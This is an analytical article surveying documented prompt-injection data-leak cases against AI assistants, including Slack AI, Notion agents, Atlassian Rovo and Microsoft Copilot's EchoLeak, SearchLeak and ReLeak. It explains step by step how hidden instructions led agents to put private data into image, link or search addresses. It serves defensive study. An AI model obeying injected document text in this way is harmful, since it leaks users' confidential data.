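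The model only writes text. The browser sends the data, just as it would request a harmless image. As OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains, a website always receives the address that was requested and commonly logs it. A product can therefore leak data even if its developer truthfully says that the model has no internet access.

In *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, on Embrace The Red, Johann Rehberger recalls reporting this channel to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. Microsoft generally blocked images in Bing Chat that May. In December, OpenAI made ChatGPT check whether an image was "safe" before displaying it. In *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, Willison (2023) welcomed the change but found it "a bit weird" that OpenAI had not simply blocked images from other sites.

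Also in December 2023, the AI security firm PromptArmor published *Data Exfiltration from Writer.com via Indirect Prompt Injection*, which describes an attack on Writer.com, where companies draft documents with an AI assistant. In PromptArmor's example, a user uploaded a file of client data, added a web page as a source and asked for a report. White text on the web page made the assistant add an image whose address contained the whole file. The file held invented Social Security numbers, revenue figures and salaries, and all of it reached the researchers' server.

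Writer restricted images with a content security policy, a list of the sites from which a browser may load material for a page. But the list allowed every address ending in cloudfront.net, the domain of a file-distribution service that Amazon rents to anyone, and the researchers received the data at one of those addresses.

In January 2026, Willison described a similar gap in Superhuman AI, an email assistant. Its policy allowed images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms, and a form can save data included in a web address. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, an injection in one email made the assistant submit the content of dozens of others to the attacker's form. The policy didn't block this because the browser contacted only Google.

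A list of trusted sites can also fail if a site on it redirects visitors elsewhere. OpenAI notes that many legitimate websites do this, so a request to a trusted address can end up at the attacker's.

Developers can overlook images that don't arrive as Markdown. *Takedown* (2025) found that one coding agent's built-in diagram feature could include an image from any web address. The agent asked for approval before some actions, but the diagram software did not. A developer who blocks images in the chat window also has to find every other place where the product draws the model's output.

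### Links and link previews

A link can carry a record in its address just as an image can, but the browser normally doesn't request that address until the user clicks. The attacker has to give the user a reason to click, and can use any visible text for the link.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes how an attack on Slack's assistant worked in August 2024. A developer had stored an API key, a kind of password for software, in a private Slack channel. The attacker had an account in the same workspace but could not open that channel. Instead, they created a public channel with no other members and posted instructions there for how Slack's assistant should answer anyone who asked for the key.

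When the developer asked the assistant for the key, retrieval found both messages. Slack searches all public channels for every user, including channels the user has never joined. The assistant replied with a false error message and a link inviting the developer to log in again. The link's address contained the key, so clicking it would have sent the key to the attacker.

The developer had little chance of tracing the answer to the attacker's message. The assistant cited only the private channel as its source, and the message did not appear on the first page of search results. In a second test, where the link led to an ordinary phishing page, the assistant did cite the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that the citations were partly random.

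In chat tools, a link can leak data without anyone clicking it. When someone posts a link in Slack, Discord or Telegram, the app may fetch the address to show a title and a picture. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do*, credits Rehberger with pointing out that the fetch also sends out any private data in the address. An assistant that posts its answers as chat messages can therefore leak data as soon as it responds.

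PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* tested this with OpenClaw, the continuously running agent that Niu and colleagues also studied. OpenClaw was exposed with its default Telegram settings. Turning off link previews stopped the leak, even though the agent's answer still contained the link. The chat app made the request, so people who examine only the agent would miss this risk.

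### Web search as a way out

A search tool sends words to a search engine and gives the model the results. If an attacker gets the model to search for "Marlow Dairy 48000", the search engine's operator receives those words, but the attacker doesn't. If the tool can also open web addresses, the attacker can obtain private text by having the model build an address from it, as in the image attack, and having the tool request that address.

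The request may come from the vendor's server rather than the user's browser. A content security policy can't block such a request, because only browsers enforce those policies. The answer may also look normal to the user.

*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) describes a test in which researchers built a small agent with access to internal company data and a web search tool. They copied part of Wikipedia's article on artificial intelligence into a blog post and added a hidden injection. When a user asked the agent to summarize the post, the agent looked up sensitive company data and sent it to the researchers' server with the same tool it had used to read the post.

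Notion put such a tool in a commercial product in September 2025, when it released Notion 3.0 with agents that could read a workspace, update databases and work on a schedule. Almost immediately, Abi Raghuram of the security company CodeIntegrity published the attack that Schneier wrote about.

Raghuram prepared a PDF that looked like a report on customer feedback. It contained white text on a white background, written to resemble a company's internal work instructions. According to The Decoder's *Notion AI agents get security update after potential data leak* (2025), the user only had to upload the PDF and ask the agent to summarize it. The agent then did the following:

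1. It opened a page in the workspace that listed the company's clients.
2. It copied out details, including each client's name and annual recurring revenue, and joined them into one string.
3. It added the string to a web address that the PDF presented as an internal company system.
4. It gave that address to the search tool, which requested it and so delivered the client list to the attacker's server.

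The agent ran on Claude Sonnet 4, then one of the strongest models available. The client list, the stranger's PDF and the search tool together made up the "lethal trifecta" that Willison had described three months earlier.

In *The Hidden Risk in Notion 3.0 AI Agents*, Willison suggested that Notion could close this channel for now by making the search tool accept only search terms. That would have stopped Raghuram's attack even if the model followed the injected instructions. But Notion also let users connect agents to GitHub, Gmail and Jira, and Willison warned that data might leave through any of these too.

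Notion responded within days. It told The Decoder that it had improved its detection of injections, including those hidden in attached files. Users would also have to approve any suspicious or model-generated link before an agent opened it. Administrators could set a policy for such links or turn off the agents' web access.

The rule on links is the stronger of these measures because nobody has to recognize the injection to apply it. Any address the model has just assembled is suspect, whatever the reason. But the rule depends on Notion asking users for approval before any data leaves, and on users reading what they approve.

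Notion also says that it is responsible for the safety of its agents and that customers are responsible for their settings on external content. It advises customers to check files before uploading them, especially files from strangers. But a person who read all the visible text in Raghuram's PDF would have found only a customer feedback report.

### What Atlassian's web search setting left on

Atlassian's assistant, Rovo, works across the company's Confluence wiki and its task tracker, Jira, and can read other services that a customer connects. Administrators can turn off web search for their whole organization and might expect this to keep Rovo from contacting strangers' websites.

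PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* found in 2026 that hidden text in an uploaded document could make Rovo send workspace data to an attacker. In the demonstration, a user uploads a document called "Backlog Guide" and asks Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. To do this, Rovo searches Jira and Confluence. The hidden text then leads it to add what it has found to the attacker's web address and open that address. Rovo needs no approval to open it, and a user who returns to the chat later sees only suggested changes to the tickets.

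Rovo had one tool for searching the web and another for opening a URL. The setting turned off only the search tool. Nothing checked whether Rovo had composed the URL itself, a check Notion had promised the previous September.

Turning off web search still kept hostile web pages from reaching Rovo through a search. But the setting controlled where Rovo looked for information, and administrators could easily mistake it for a control on where Rovo could send information. The Hacker News (2026) notes that Atlassian's documentation for the setting does not cover addresses that Rovo composes and opens on its own. It also cautions that only PromptArmor has reported the bypass.

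Varonis, another security company, found a different way into Rovo at about the same time. A link to Rovo could include a prompt, which appeared in the chat when someone opened the link. An attacker could therefore put instructions in a link to a company's real Rovo page and send it to an employee. A single click on the link made Rovo carry out the instructions with the employee's access.

In a test, Varonis used an image address to send out a private API key stored in Confluence. According to The Hacker News, the same method was tried on Jira and on data from Microsoft's SharePoint and Outlook. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* reports that Varonis named the flaw RovoBlast and presented it at the DEF CON security conference in August.

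RovoBlast would be a problem even for a model that could perfectly distinguish a user's request from the text of a document, because the attacker's words arrived where the user's own words belong. Atlassian fixed this in ordinary code by changing how Rovo handled links, and customers didn't have to install anything.

### A request for approval after the data had gone

In January 2026, PromptArmor showed that Notion AI could leak data even when it asked for the user's approval. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes a recruiter who uploads a candidate's résumé and asks the assistant to update notes in a hiring tracker. The résumé contains an injection in one-point white type, covered by a white image.

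The injection made the assistant collect all the text in the tracker, attach it to the attacker's address and insert an image with that address into the page. Notion then asked the user whether to trust the external site. The address in the warning contained text from the tracker, so an attentive user had a fair chance of noticing that something was wrong. By then it no longer mattered, because events happened in this order:

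1. The assistant edited the page, and Notion saved the edit.
2. The user's browser found the new image in the page and requested it, which sent the tracker's text to the attacker.
3. Notion asked the user for approval.

The attacker received the data whether the user accepted or refused. The data included salary expectations, comments on candidates, internal details of the role, and diversity hiring goals.

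Asking for approval after an edit is good enough in most cases, because the user can reject a bad rewrite and get the old paragraph back. Notion's design would have been reasonable if edits could affect only the page. But displaying an image from another site sends that site a request, and restoring the page does not undo the request. To protect the tracker, Notion had to hold back either the edit or the image until the user had answered.

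A busy recruiter might have approved even a well-timed request without reading it. But a recruiter who saw colleagues' comments about a candidate in an unfamiliar web address might well have rejected it. The actual design gave even a careful user no way to prevent the theft.

The September safeguards did not close this channel. Turning off web search would not have blocked the image, since the browser requested it. Notion also had a language model scan uploaded documents and warn about suspicious ones. PromptArmor argues that an injection could cause the scanning model to label a document safe, but its researchers focused on how data gets out rather than on evading the scan. They add that web pages, Notion pages and connected mail did not appear to be scanned.

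They found a smaller version of the flaw in Notion Mail, whose drafting assistant displayed images from other sites inside draft emails. If a user asked for a draft based on one trusted and one untrusted page, the untrusted page could send out the contents of the trusted one. The assistant seemed able to use only the pages the user had mentioned, so it could leak much less.

Notion fixed the page-editing flaw on the night of January 7, 2026. PromptArmor had recommended blocking images from other sites until the user approves them and setting a strict content security policy. PromptArmor's timeline does not record which fix Notion chose, or whether Notion also changed the Mail assistant.

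### What the vendors disputed

In four of these cases, PromptArmor reported the flaw privately before publishing it. Three of the vendors rejected the report or found its evidence insufficient, then fixed the product within days of publication.

| Product | Time from report to publication | Response before publication | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|
| Writer.com (2023) | 16 days | Not a security issue | Within 4 days of publication |
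| Slack AI (2024) | 6 days | Evidence insufficient | Day of publication |
| Notion AI, page edits (2026) | 14 days | Closed as "Not Applicable" | Night of publication |
| Atlassian Rovo, uploaded file (2026) | 74 days | Case number and thanks | None confirmed by August 8 |

Writer objected that real customers' accounts could not open any website, which would have kept the hostile page away from the assistant. PromptArmor replied that paid accounts had the same flaw. Writer did not answer or publish evidence for its claim. Soon after the attack became public, Writer's assistant could no longer display images or clickable links.

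Slack disputed what the demonstration proved, replying that the information in the first video had been posted in a public channel and that letting every member search public channels was "intended behavior". This policy is sensible for the messages themselves, but it doesn't answer the complaint, because only the attacker's instructions were in a public channel. The key was in a private channel that the attacker could not read. Slack's access rules worked correctly for both messages, and the leak occurred when the assistant combined them.

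After releasing a patch, Slack (2024) said that someone with an existing account in the workspace could, "under very limited and specific circumstances", phish other users for certain data, and that it had no evidence of unauthorized access to customers' data. Slack's description of the circumstances is fair for the attack PromptArmor tested, which needed an insider, a question about the right subject and a click.

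Slack began including uploaded files in the assistant's answers on August 14, the day it received PromptArmor's report. If a user uploaded a stranger's PDF, the stranger might not need an account to carry out the attack. PromptArmor had finished testing before the change and didn't try this version, but called it highly likely. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* also describes the risk from files as a warning from the researchers, separate from the attack they had carried out.

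The Notion dispute arose largely because HackerOne, the platform that runs Notion's bug bounty, did not pass on a report. HackerOne staff screened the report and closed it before Notion's team had seen it. PromptArmor published no explanation from them. The report showed "data leaked outside of the workspace", which Notion's rules at the time gave as an example of the security impact a prompt injection report had to show.

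The rules also made the mistake harder to correct. Under a version dated December 16, eight days before the report, Notion would not review closed reports sent to its security address "under any circumstances", and researchers had to ask HackerOne to mediate instead. PromptArmor's timeline lists no such request, and Notion contacted the researchers directly on the day they went public. The report arrived on Christmas Eve, which may partly explain the poor screening.

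Atlassian did not publicly dispute the uploaded-file attack. The Hacker News reports that PromptArmor reported the attack on May 23, received a case number two days later, wrote again on June 4 and July 29, and heard nothing more before publishing on August 5. Atlassian accepted the RovoBlast report through the bounty platform Bugcrowd, paid $6,000 and fixed the flaw on July 8, a month before Varonis published. Neither company has said whether that fix also affected the uploaded-file attack.

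Superhuman recognized this kind of flaw without dispute. Willison credits the company with treating the theft of email through Google Forms as a high-priority incident and fixing the flaw.

### Test data, uploads and commercial interest

Researchers staged all of these attacks, mostly with invented data in accounts they controlled. The Hacker News found no report of anyone using either Rovo attack against a real organization, and Slack reported no sign of misuse. The demonstrations show that data could get out, but not how reliably the attacks worked. The published accounts of the product attacks give no success rates, and screenshots of a successful attempt don't show how many others failed.

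PromptArmor, which published most of these cases, sells a service that monitors the AI products its customers buy. It benefits from alarming headlines, and its choice of products is little evidence of how common such flaws are. For example, it calls the Rovo attack "zero-click", but The Hacker News points out that the victim still has to give Rovo the file and make a request. The demonstration supports the more modest claim that Rovo sends the data without asking for approval.

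The vendors' repairs are better evidence that these problems were real than the researchers' descriptions of them. Slack and Notion confirmed that they had fixed the problems PromptArmor reported, and Writer removed the features the attack used. No similar confirmation exists for the bypass of Rovo's web search setting.

Both Notion attacks and the first Rovo attack began when a user uploaded a file. The need for an upload protects someone who works only with colleagues' documents, but it does little for a recruiter, whose job is to open strangers' files. PromptArmor says the hostile text could also come from a web page, a connected service or, in Rovo's case, a customer's support ticket. That is plausible, but the published demonstrations used uploads. An attack through a support ticket would be considerably worse, because the customer could put the text into the company's system without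 an employee uploading it.

Private text from these tools can also leak without prompt injection. In November 2026, Notion warned customers about a breach at Fireworks AI, one of its suppliers. *Notion Customer Data Compromised in Fireworks AI Hack* (Arghire, 2026) reports that the attackers accessed chat transcripts from fewer than 1 percent of Notion workspaces, and that most transcripts could not be linked to a particular customer. Blocking images and web search in Notion would not have protected transcripts held by the supplier.

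## Repeated data leaks in Microsoft Copilot, 2025 to 2026

Slack, Notion and Writer each closed the channel through which a researcher had shown data could leak. It is easier to judge whether such fixes eventually make a product safe in the case of Microsoft's Copilot, which has been through several rounds of reports and fixes. Between January 2025 and November 2026, security companies reported, and Microsoft fixed, at least seven ways for an outsider to take data out of Copilot.

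The name "Microsoft Copilot" covers two products. Microsoft 365 Copilot is the workplace assistant, which can search an employee's mail and Teams chats and the company's files. The consumer Copilot, also called Copilot Personal, is for individuals, who can connect it to other services they use, such as Gmail.

### EchoLeak

Aim Labs, the research department of Aim Security, found that an outsider could steal data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending an employee a single email. Ravia (2025) describes the attack for Aim in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*. Willison, in a post of the same name, writes that Aim reported the flaw in January 2025 and that Microsoft had rolled out a fix by the time Aim published in June. The flaw is numbered CVE-2025-32711, and INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists its CVSS score as 9.3 (Critical) in *CVE-2025-32711*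 (2025).

The attack combined an injection with several ordinary gaps in Microsoft's software:

1. The attacker emails an employee. The message is long and has sections on common office subjects, such as onboarding and leave, with the same instructions in each.
2. The employee later asks Copilot about one of those subjects. Retrieval finds the matching section and selects it along with internal material.
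3. Microsoft's injection filter, a classifier meant to keep hostile text away from the model, lets the email through. Aim had phrased the instructions as if they were for the human recipient and had avoided any mention of AI.
4. The model picks out the most sensitive information in its context and writes it into the address of an image. Copilot normally deleted images and links that pointed outside the company, but it recognized only the usual Markdown notation, and Aim used a less common one.
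5. The employee's browser tries to load the image. Microsoft let the browser load images only from a list of approved sites, which did not include Aim's server. But one approved address, belonging to Teams, would fetch any other web address it was given. The browser contacted Teams, and Teams passed the data on to Aim.

The injection also told Copilot not to mention the email, so the employee would not see it among the sources.

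Microsoft's safeguards made the attack harder. Aim's first version used a link that the employee had to click. The second used an image loaded through SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, and worked only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Aim had to search the approved sites until it found the Teams address, which worked without any action from anyone.

The employee still has to ask Copilot something that leads it to retrieve the email, so Ravia's claim that the attack does not rely on specific user behavior is slightly too strong. Ravia concedes that an email about a single subject would have a "relatively poor retrieval rate". Covering many subjects raised the rate, but Ravia gives no figure for how often the finished attack worked.

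Ravia proposes the term "LLM scope violation" for the central step, in which text from outside the company leads the model to use data from inside it. This is another case of the confused deputy, but Ravia also makes a new practical suggestion. He suggests that a filter look for text that refers to information beyond itself, because the email's wording could otherwise pass for a note to a colleague. Aim was selling a product based on this idea. Such a filter might have caught EchoLeak, but many honest emails also refer to information beyond themselves, such as a customer's request to "please send me the figures we discussed".

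According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that the flaw had affected no customers. SiliconANGLE (2025) reported more cautiously that Microsoft had found no evidence of anyone exploiting it.

### SearchLeak

A year later, Varonis got data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot through another approved Microsoft site. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot's search page, which accepts a query in its web address. Copilot ran the query as a prompt when the page opened, so an attacker could put instructions in a link to a real Microsoft address, much as Varonis did with Atlassian's Rovo. The employee had to click the link once.

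In the demonstration, the instructions told Copilot to find an email and put its subject line in the address of an image. The subject line alone can be valuable if it contains a login code. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* notes that such codes often stay valid for several minutes. Varonis says the same method could reach calendars and company files.

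Microsoft had a safeguard against images of this kind. It converted the markup in Copilot's answers into plain text, so that the browser would show the code for an image instead of loading the image. But Copilot displays an answer while it is still writing it, and the safeguard ran at the end:

1. Copilot wrote the part of the answer that contained the image.
2. The browser displayed that part and immediately requested the image.
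3. Copilot finished writing, and the safeguard converted the answer to plain text.

The data had leaked by the third step. Notion made a similar mistake when its assistant saved an edit before asking the user to approve it. Varonis recommends sanitizing each piece of an answer before the browser displays it.

The image request still had to go to a site on the approved list. Microsoft's search engine, Bing, was on the list, and its search for similar pictures has Bing's servers fetch a picture from an address the user supplies. Varonis supplied an address on its own server that contained the stolen title, so Bing's servers sent Varonis the title when they requested the picture.

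The list of approved sites that Ravia published in 2025 had fewer than 30 distinct entries, and Bing was already one of them. Microsoft had just learned from EchoLeak that an approved site could pass data on to an unapproved one. Varonis now advises companies to check such lists for any site that fetches addresses on a visitor's behalf. If Microsoft had done that thoroughly after EchoLeak, it would probably have found the Bing feature.

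Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), published on June 4, lists SearchLeak as CVE-2026-42824 and says that Microsoft has fully mitigated it and knows of no exploitation. Microsoft rated the flaw Critical, although its published scale for AI flaws would rate data theft that requires a click as only Important. The flaw's CVSS score was a modest 6.5, which reflects that an attack requires a click and exposes data but does no other damage.

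The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reports that the US National Vulnerability Database scored the same flaw at 7.5. The Next Web disputes this and says the database also shows 6.5. The scoring formula gives 7.5 if an analyst decides that the victim doesn't have to do anything and keeps every other input the same, so the whole difference could come from whether the analyst counts the victim's one click.

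### Reprompt and CoSnitch

Varonis also found two flaws in the consumer Copilot that could be exploited when a user clicked a link to a real Microsoft address. It reported one of them, Reprompt, in August 2025, and Microsoft patched it in January 2026, according to The Next Web. *Reprompt* (Taler, 2026) describes an attack chain that could steal a user's personal data after that one click. Varonis got past Copilot's safeguards by having it make the same request twice.

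Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes the other flaw, CVE-2026-24301. An undocumented setting in the link made Copilot run the attacker's prompt as soon as the page loaded. Copilot then searched the victim's connected accounts, built a web address from what it found and opened that address with the tool it uses to summarize web pages. In one test it retrieved a password from the text of an email. In a separate part of the research, a web page planted instructions in Copilot's memory when a user asked for a summary.

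The researchers learned about the undocumented setting from Copilot. They asked it why a link couldn't run a prompt automatically, then kept asking about the reasons it gave. Copilot eventually named the setting and said Microsoft had disabled it, but the setting worked when the researchers tried it.

Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it on August 18, 2026. The flaw affected only the consumer Copilot, according to the United Nations University (UNU). TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* gives its severity as 8.8. SearchLeak scored only 6.5, even though it exposed company mail and files and also took one click. CoSnitch's ability to alter Copilot's memory may account for some of the gap, but the scores are a poor guide to which flaw a company should have worried about more.

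### ReLeak

On December 3, 2026, the team that found EchoLeak published three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. The team had become Cato AI Labs after the network security company Cato Networks bought Aim in September 2025. Cato's *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents the attacks as a sequel, one year after EchoLeak. The fullest press accounts are *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* ("You don't even have to open the email") (Antipov, 2026) and *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026).

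All three attacks start as EchoLeak did. An outsider sends an employee an email with hidden instructions, and the attack works even if the email stays unread. When the employee asks Copilot an ordinary work question, Copilot retrieves the email and follows the instructions, using the employee's access to gather private data. Microsoft's injection protections failed to stop any of the three. The attacks differ in how they send the data out.

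**Images fetched by Bing (CVE-2026-124115).** Copilot put confidential data in the address of an image in its answer. The employee's browser loaded the image automatically, and Bing forwarded the data to the attacker's server. Antipov describes the channel as similar to SearchLeak's, except that SearchLeak needed a click. Microsoft recorded SearchLeak as fully mitigated on June 4, and Cato reported its Bing attack eight to eleven weeks later. Cato may have used a different Bing feature or found a gap in the fix. In either case, Microsoft had closed the path Varonis used, but Bing was still unsafe to leave on the list.

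**Files that Copilot created (CVE-2026-124132).** Copilot can save its work as a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file. The injection made it create a file containing a link with confidential data in its address. Microsoft's servers process files in OneDrive and SharePoint in the background, and while doing so they sent the data out. In Cato's tests this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation had ended, even if nobody opened the file.

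This attack avoids most of the protections that EchoLeak and SearchLeak had to bypass. A safeguard that cleans Copilot's answers has nothing to remove, because the address is in a file. The list of approved sites doesn't apply, because the request comes from a server instead of the employee's browser. An employee who noticed something odd could not have stopped the attack by closing the chat.

**The code sandbox (CVE-2026-78501).** Copilot can write and run Python programs, for example to analyze a spreadsheet. It runs them in an isolated environment called a sandbox. According to Microsoft's documentation, no network traffic can enter or leave the sandbox. Cato got around that restriction, and a program in the sandbox then sent confidential data directly to an outside server.

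Microsoft rated the sandbox flaw Critical. Its CVSS score was at first 7.4 and is now 8.6. Neither Antipov nor Faisal explains the change, but for a flaw that exposes a lot of data beyond the affected component, the CVSS formula gives 7.4 if the victim has to do something and 8.6 if not. If that is why the score changed, Microsoft decided in this case that asking Copilot a question does not count as user interaction, which its severity scale leaves unclear. Scores for the other two flaws were not yet public in early December.

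Cato reported the flaws between July 29 and August 20. Microsoft fixed the sandbox flaw on September 17, the generated-file flaw on November 11 and the Bing image flaw on November 15. It made all three fixes on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. The sandbox is also available to agents that customers build with Microsoft's Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, but nobody has confirmed that the attack worked there.

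Another team broke out of Copilot's sandbox that summer. Lahav (2026), in *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate*, describes an attack that the data security company Rubrik published on August 6. When a user asks Copilot about a malicious document, the attacker gains a live connection to the chat and can send prompts, read Copilot's answers and decide what to ask next. The attacker could therefore see what data is available before choosing what to steal, which an EchoLeak attacker has to specify in advance in the email. Knight (2026), in *AI sandbox escape uncovered in Microsoft Copilot flaw*, reports that a single Word document was enough to get from the sandbox into Azure, Microsoft's cloud platform.

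In its dispute with John Russell that January, Microsoft said that running commands in Copilot's isolated environment did not cross a security boundary. That was a fair answer as long as the environment was really isolated, but by August two teams had shown ways out of it.

### The seven attacks compared

Cato's report dates are public only as a range, so the repair times for ReLeak are ranges too.

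| Attack | Entry point | Clicks needed | Outward channel | Time to fix | Known exploitation |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Outsider's email | None | Image, fetched through Teams | About 5 months | None, according to Microsoft |
| Reprompt (consumer) | Link containing a prompt | One | Requests to the attacker's server | About 5 months | None reported |
| SearchLeak | Link containing a prompt | One | Image, fetched through Bing | Fixed by June 4, 2026 | None, according to Microsoft |
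| CoSnitch (consumer) | Link containing a prompt | One | Web address opened by Copilot | About 8 months | None seen by Varonis |
| ReLeak: images | Outsider's email | None | Image, fetched through Bing | 87 to 109 days | None known to Cato |
| ReLeak: files | Outsider's email | None | Link in a generated file, fetched by Microsoft's servers | 83 to 105 days | None known to Cato |
| ReLeak: sandbox | Outsider's email | None | Direct connection from a program | 28 to 50 days | None known to Cato |

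The table leaves out several flaws with less detailed public records. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes how Johann Rehberger extracted data through Copilot's preview of web code. He reported the problem in 2025, and Microsoft has since patched it. STAR Labs' *CVE-2025-59252* (2025) lists a Copilot flaw from October 2025 with the same 9.3 severity score as EchoLeak. GCVE's *CVE-2026-26133* (2026) records an "AI command injection" from March 2026, and INCIBE's *CVE-2026-26164* (2026) records another injection flaw from May. Microsoft describes each of the last three flaws in one sentence, too little to tell whether a stranger's email or document could have triggered it.

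### The case that the repairs are working

Microsoft fixed all seven flaws, and nobody has reported a victim. The people who found the flaws in the table told Microsoft privately and published their findings once a fix was available. The March 2026 flaw affected versions of the Android app that users had to replace, but the other fixes didn't require customers to install anything. Those fixes avoided a common problem with older kinds of software, where attackers can keep using a known flaw against every company that hasn't installed the patch.

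The claim that nobody was harmed depends on who could have noticed, and few customers could have detected either attack. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), a Brazilian article on digital forensics, suggests that investigators compare emails from outside the company with Copilot's searches, the image addresses in its answers and the requests leaving the company's browsers. In the Bing attack, the browser records would show a visit to Bing, which looks normal. In the attack that used generated files, they would show nothing, because the browser made no request.

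Microsoft could see more, because its servers made the final request to the attacker in EchoLeak, SearchLeak and two of the ReLeak attacks. Its statements about EchoLeak and SearchLeak are therefore some evidence, although the published versions don't explain how Microsoft checked. The evidence about ReLeak's effect on customers is weaker. Faisal's introduction says Microsoft reported that no customers were affected, but the article itself attributes the statement to Cato, which doesn't run Copilot and can't see most of its traffic.

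The growing number of reports is not evidence that Copilot has become less safe, either. For transparency, Microsoft publishes records of flaws it has already fixed on its servers, some of which would otherwise never have become public. Researchers have also become better at searching for flaws. For ReLeak, Cato's staff directed AI agents that wrote test cases, analyzed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. More searching would turn up more flaws even in a product that was slowly improving.

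### The case that the weakness remains

Cato, quoted by Faisal, says that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak, and comparing EchoLeak with ReLeak supports this. In 2025, Copilot followed instructions in a stranger's unread email, and Microsoft's filter did not stop it. The same was true in the summer of 2026, after more than a year of changes to the defenses. Microsoft had repaired the route by which data leaked out but had not stopped attackers' instructions from reaching Copilot.

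Faisal attributes the repeated leaks to Copilot's new abilities, since displaying images, writing files and running code each gave data another way to leave. That explains the leaks through generated files and the sandbox, but not the one through Bing, which was on the approved list all along. Microsoft could have found the Bing channel by checking a short list after EchoLeak, but it can find a leak in a new feature only by checking, before release, whether anything the feature does can cause a request to an outside server. This can be hard to determine, as with the generated files, where the request came from a background process with no obvious connection to Copilot.

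EchoLeak and SearchLeak became public a year apart, and Reprompt affected a different product from either of them. These facts don't support The Next Web's description of the three as "three disclosures in six months", each of which got past protections that the previous fix was supposed to provide. The three attacks that began with a link have a simpler cause than EchoLeak, and Microsoft can remove that cause with ordinary code, as Atlassian did for Rovo. Copilot only has to show the prompt and wait for the user to submit it.

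Even so, Microsoft was slow to apply that remedy everywhere. When it patched Reprompt in January 2026, it had known about CoSnitch for about a month, but a link could still run a prompt in the same product until August. Varonis was surprised that the technique also worked on the workplace version, which was supposed to have stronger safeguards.

For about 15 months, Microsoft always had at least one reported but unrepaired flaw that let attackers take data out of one of its two Copilots. Reprompt was open from August 2025 to January 2026, CoSnitch from December 2025 to August 2026, and the ReLeak flaws from late July 2026 or earlier to November 15. Customers who used only the workplace version were exposed to fewer of these flaws, but they had no way of knowing about them. Anyone who found the same flaws independently could have used them until they were repaired.

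Judging by these cases, fixing individual leaks has protected customers from the attacks that researchers found first, but it has not removed the underlying problem. Attacks that need a click and the misuse of approved sites both look fixable. Zero-click attacks will probably continue as long as Copilot retrieves strangers' email into the same context as company data and keeps gaining features that can contact other servers. Microsoft could close each of these channels without removing anything employees use, but it has not managed to do the same for the Word documents that infect one another.

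## Do attackers use it outside research?

Researchers found all seven Copilot attacks, and nobody has reported a victim of any of them. Even if the flaws are real, criminals may not bother to exploit them.

### The skeptic's argument

Researchers have been publishing prompt injections since 2022 and find them easily. *The Summer of Johann* (Willison, 2025) describes how Johann Rehberger published one report a day in August 2025, each on a product vulnerable to the same well-known problems. Most of the products were coding tools, so the reports provide little evidence about document assistants, but they show how much one person can find. A skeptic would expect attackers to have used such flaws by now if they were worth using.

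As of December 5, 2026, no public report appears to confirm that anyone outside research has stolen data by injecting instructions into a document or email assistant. Some accounts make research sound like real attacks. *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) has a headline about a "campaign" that "looks to steal data from victims", but the campaign is ReLeak, which was Cato's research. *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier* (Chang, Bao and colleagues, 2026), an academic paper, lists EchoLeak among "real-world incidents", though EchoLeak was also a demonstration.

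*First Agentic AI Data Breach Reported to Spanish Regulator* (Townsend, 2026) describes a breach in which an AI agent allegedly logged in to a system, found a vulnerability and accessed personal data. The agent was the intruder, rather than a company's own assistant that had been tricked into giving data away.

Skeptics argue that criminals have easier methods. *Notes from Underground*, published in July 2026 by the email security company Proofpoint, reports that criminals have turned to attacking AI systems less than many security leaders expected. It speculates that they have little reason to change while targeting people "is still highly effective". A phishing email can work on anyone with an inbox, whereas an injection works only on people who use a vulnerable assistant, and the vendor can stop it for all of them at once by changing its own servers. Google adds that misled AI systems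 often used to fail to carry out an attacker's instructions, so the effort was unlikely to be worthwhile.

### Companies that want assistants to recommend them

The clearest case of real use is the "Summarize with AI" buttons mentioned earlier, which ordinary businesses put on their websites. Each button is a link that opens the visitor's assistant with a prompt already filled in. The prompt contains a request to summarize the page and an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source or recommend it in future conversations. Microsoft named this practice "AI recommendation poisoning" in February 2026.

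Microsoft reviewed AI-related links in email traffic over 60 days. It found 50 different prompts of this kind from 31 companies in more than a dozen industries, including health, finance and legal services. All were real businesses, and one sold security products. The most aggressive prompts tried to store whole passages of marketing copy. Microsoft traced the trend to free tools advertised as a way to "build presence in AI memory". These tools let a website owner add such a button by installing a plugin.

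These are counts of attempts. Microsoft says the effect varied between assistants and over time, and that it could no longer reproduce some earlier results in Copilot. It doesn't say how many people clicked the buttons or how many assistants saved the memory. Its example of a finance chief who commits millions to a supplier because of a planted recommendation is hypothetical.

People outside research do use prompt injection, but mostly for a mild purpose. The companies had a cheap method, little fear of arrest and a clear reason to want a small bias in their favor. A biased answer could still do serious harm if it concerns a medical treatment or someone's savings. Microsoft also warns that an assistant told to trust a website may also trust comments that strangers leave there.

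### Injected text on the public web

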